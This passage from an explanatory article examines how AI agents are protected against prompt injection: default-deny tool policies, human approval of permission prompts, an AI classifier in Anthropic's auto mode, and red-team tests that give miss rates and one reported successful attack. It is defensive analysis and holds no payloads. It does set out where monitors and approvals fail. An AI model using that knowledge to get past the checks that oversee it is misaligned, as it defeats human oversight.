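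Meta's rule would count the altered document as a change, but it would still permit an agent to read hostile text and make changes if the agent has no sensitive access. An agent that only scores strangers' papers has just one of the properties, yet its judgment can still be manipulated. Counting properties within a session also misses an injection that stays in the agent's memory until a later session with different tools. The objection is correct that neither rule is sufficient, but both would have prevented some of the worst attacks, such as EchoLeak.

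Under default-deny, the system refuses every tool call unless a rule allows it. Guidance published in September 2026 by AWS and the SANS Institute, a security training organisation, calls this the most critical architectural pattern for securing agents, according to Help Net Security's *Your AI agent’s system prompt is not a security control*. The guidance also warns against giving one agent all three parts of the trifecta. It recommends sending high-impact actions to a person for approval, however confident the model is, and letting the agent retrieve only what its user could open. Companies can do much of this with the access controls they already run, and NIST, the American standards institute, published its guide to one kind, attribute-based access control, in 2014.

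Help Net Security reports that OWASP, which publishes widely used rankings of software risks, ranks prompt injection first among threats to AI applications. A company can use that ranking to decide what to worry about, but not which calls to allow. A default-deny policy doesn't settle which calls to allow either, although it makes oversights safer because the agent can't use a tool that everybody forgot about. It doesn't help in case B, because the assistant is supposed to have the payment tool.

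### What people approve

Most of these designs eventually leave some decisions to a person. The best evidence on how well that works comes from Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), which reports that users approve 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts. Most of these prompts probably concern harmless commands, so the figure alone doesn't show that users are careless.

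Anthropic therefore had a research vendor recruit 1,053 paid testers for a coding study. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not on what. Partway through each session, one permission prompt changed to show a clearly dangerous command, which never ran, and the vendor recorded the tester's answer. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused. Anthropic also ran the same commands through auto mode, which uses its classifier in place of the user's approval. Auto mode blocked 937 of them, or 89%.

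The table shows how the two overlap. Anthropic gives the totals and the two cases of disagreement, and the other two numbers follow by subtraction.

| | Tester refused | Tester approved |
|---|---|---|
| Auto mode blocked | 137 | 800 |
| Auto mode allowed | 6 | 110 |

Adding the testers' review to auto mode would have caught six more commands, raising the share caught from 89.0% to 89.6%. The testers refused about 17% of dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while auto mode's rate stayed the same.

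These testers weren't risking their own files, so developers at work may be more careful. Anthropic was also testing its own product, and the study doesn't measure how many harmless commands auto mode blocks. But the way people configure Claude Code supports the same conclusion, since a quarter of interactive sessions start with all permission checks switched off.

People are less likely to approve larger requests. Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans it shows them, though perhaps mostly because they want the work done differently. Conseca allows users to approve one set of rules per task, which is more like approving a plan than a command. Tsai and Bagdasarian expect this to tire users less, but they haven't tested whether anyone reads the rules.

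The content of the approval prompt also matters. In case B, the owner has no reason to refuse if he is asked only whether to pay the supplier this month's amount. If the prompt also shows that the account differs from the one used for the last twelve payments, and gives the phone number on file, he can check something the attacker doesn't control. Someone has to write the rule that looks up the payment history, so an approval step also depends on a good policy.

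### A model as the approver

Auto mode became the default for new Claude Code sessions on several plans in August 2026. In an update dated 22 October, Anthropic announced that most of its Claude apps would follow. If the classifier blocks three actions in a row, or twenty in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user.

Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to test the system against prompt injection. The testers ran 72 scenarios ten times each, and none of the 720 attempts succeeded against any of three Claude models in auto mode. But with auto mode switched off, only 0.09% succeeded, or about two of 2,160 attempts if each model faced all 720. The test is good evidence about the models, but they left so few attacks for auto mode to stop that the results reveal very little about the classifier.

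The same test suggests more about what an automatic reviewer can add to a weaker model. OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol fell for 19.03% of the attacks with full access to the machine and 5.83% with Codex's own review mode. (OpenAI has since released a new version of that mode.)

The attacker also did not adapt to the target. Trajectory Labs had optimised the attacks against an older Claude model, Opus 4.7. Repeated attempts at one scenario are not independent, so it is safer to count scenarios than attempts. No attack succeeded in any of the 72 scenarios, which is compatible with up to 4% of similar scenarios being vulnerable.

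In a two-week exercise with Anthropic, Apollo Research, a British AI safety organisation, tested the classifier harder by inserting synthetic attacks into recordings of real coding work. Anthropic then gave the classifier more context, such as whether a code repository is public, and the share of attacks it missed fell from 12% to 7%. Apollo had held back some of the attacks for the second round, so the improvement wasn't just memorisation. Anthropic warns that the 7% applies only to this set of attacks.

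Later in August, Johann Rehberger reported an attack on Claude Code in auto mode that he says worked in about 80% of runs. Willison has since agreed with a reader that it was not strictly a prompt injection, because the model followed no malicious instructions. The attack therefore doesn't contradict the 720 failed attempts, but it shows that they are little evidence of how well an agent resists other kinds of attack. Rehberger advises running unattended agents in a sandbox with restricted network access and keeping passwords and keys out of their reach.

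Willison accepts that auto mode is better than asking people to click "OK" every few steps, but he wants more independent tests. He also doubts that any version of it could catch setup instructions that name a malicious software package. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems. That is more reasonable than the study of testers suggests, because someone who sees two such requests a week is likely to read them more carefully than someone who has just clicked through fifty.

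### What adoption would take

Some mainstream products already enforce rules outside the model. AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026) announced such a service in March. The service sits in a gateway between agents and their tools and blocks any call that no rule permits. Customers can write the rules in Cedar or in plain English. AWS says the service translates English rules into Cedar, checks them against the tools' descriptions, and uses automated reasoning to find rules that are too loose, too strict or impossible to satisfy. AWS's *Authoring Dogwood policies from natural language in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* describes a newer policy language for which customers can import whole prose documents. Gemini CLI has fixed rules and also includes Conseca, which is off by default.

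An organization that buys one of these products still has to supply the policy. AWS expects security, compliance and operations teams to write it without touching the agent's code, but those teams need to know what each agent's job requires. Keeping the policy current may take more work than writing it, because tools and duties change. AutoCedar records which sentence in the requirements each rule came from, so when a requirement changes, a reviewer rechecks only the affected parts.

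A company would also have to label its data sources. A rule about authenticated senders is useless if the mail tool returns the sender and the message as one block of text. The labels then have to reach the monitor. Mondl and colleagues point out that Cedar is stateless, so a Cedar rule about an outgoing email can't consider a file the agent opened two calls earlier unless another component tracks it.

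Tools would have to declare what they do. A rule can limit a tool that pays a named supplier far more precisely than one that runs any shell command. Gemini CLI lets an administrator write rules that depend on a tool's own declaration that it only reads data. But whoever supplies the tool writes that declaration, so a malicious supplier could lie. Rules can also fail by accident. Google warns that an underscore in the name of an outside tool server can make security rules for that server fail without an error message.

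Finally, people would have to accept an agent that does less. The drop in completed tasks with CaMeL is an extreme example, but even modest inconvenience leads users to switch protection off, and Mondl and colleagues report that developers do the same when policies are too narrow. An administrator can remove that choice. According to Google's *Gemini CLI configuration*, one setting disables both automatic approval of everything and the "always allow" button, though it is off by default. AWS offers a gentler way to start, a mode that only logs what the rules would have refused. A company can run it for a few weeks and count how much legitimate work the policy would have blocked, before employees have a reason to look for a way around it.
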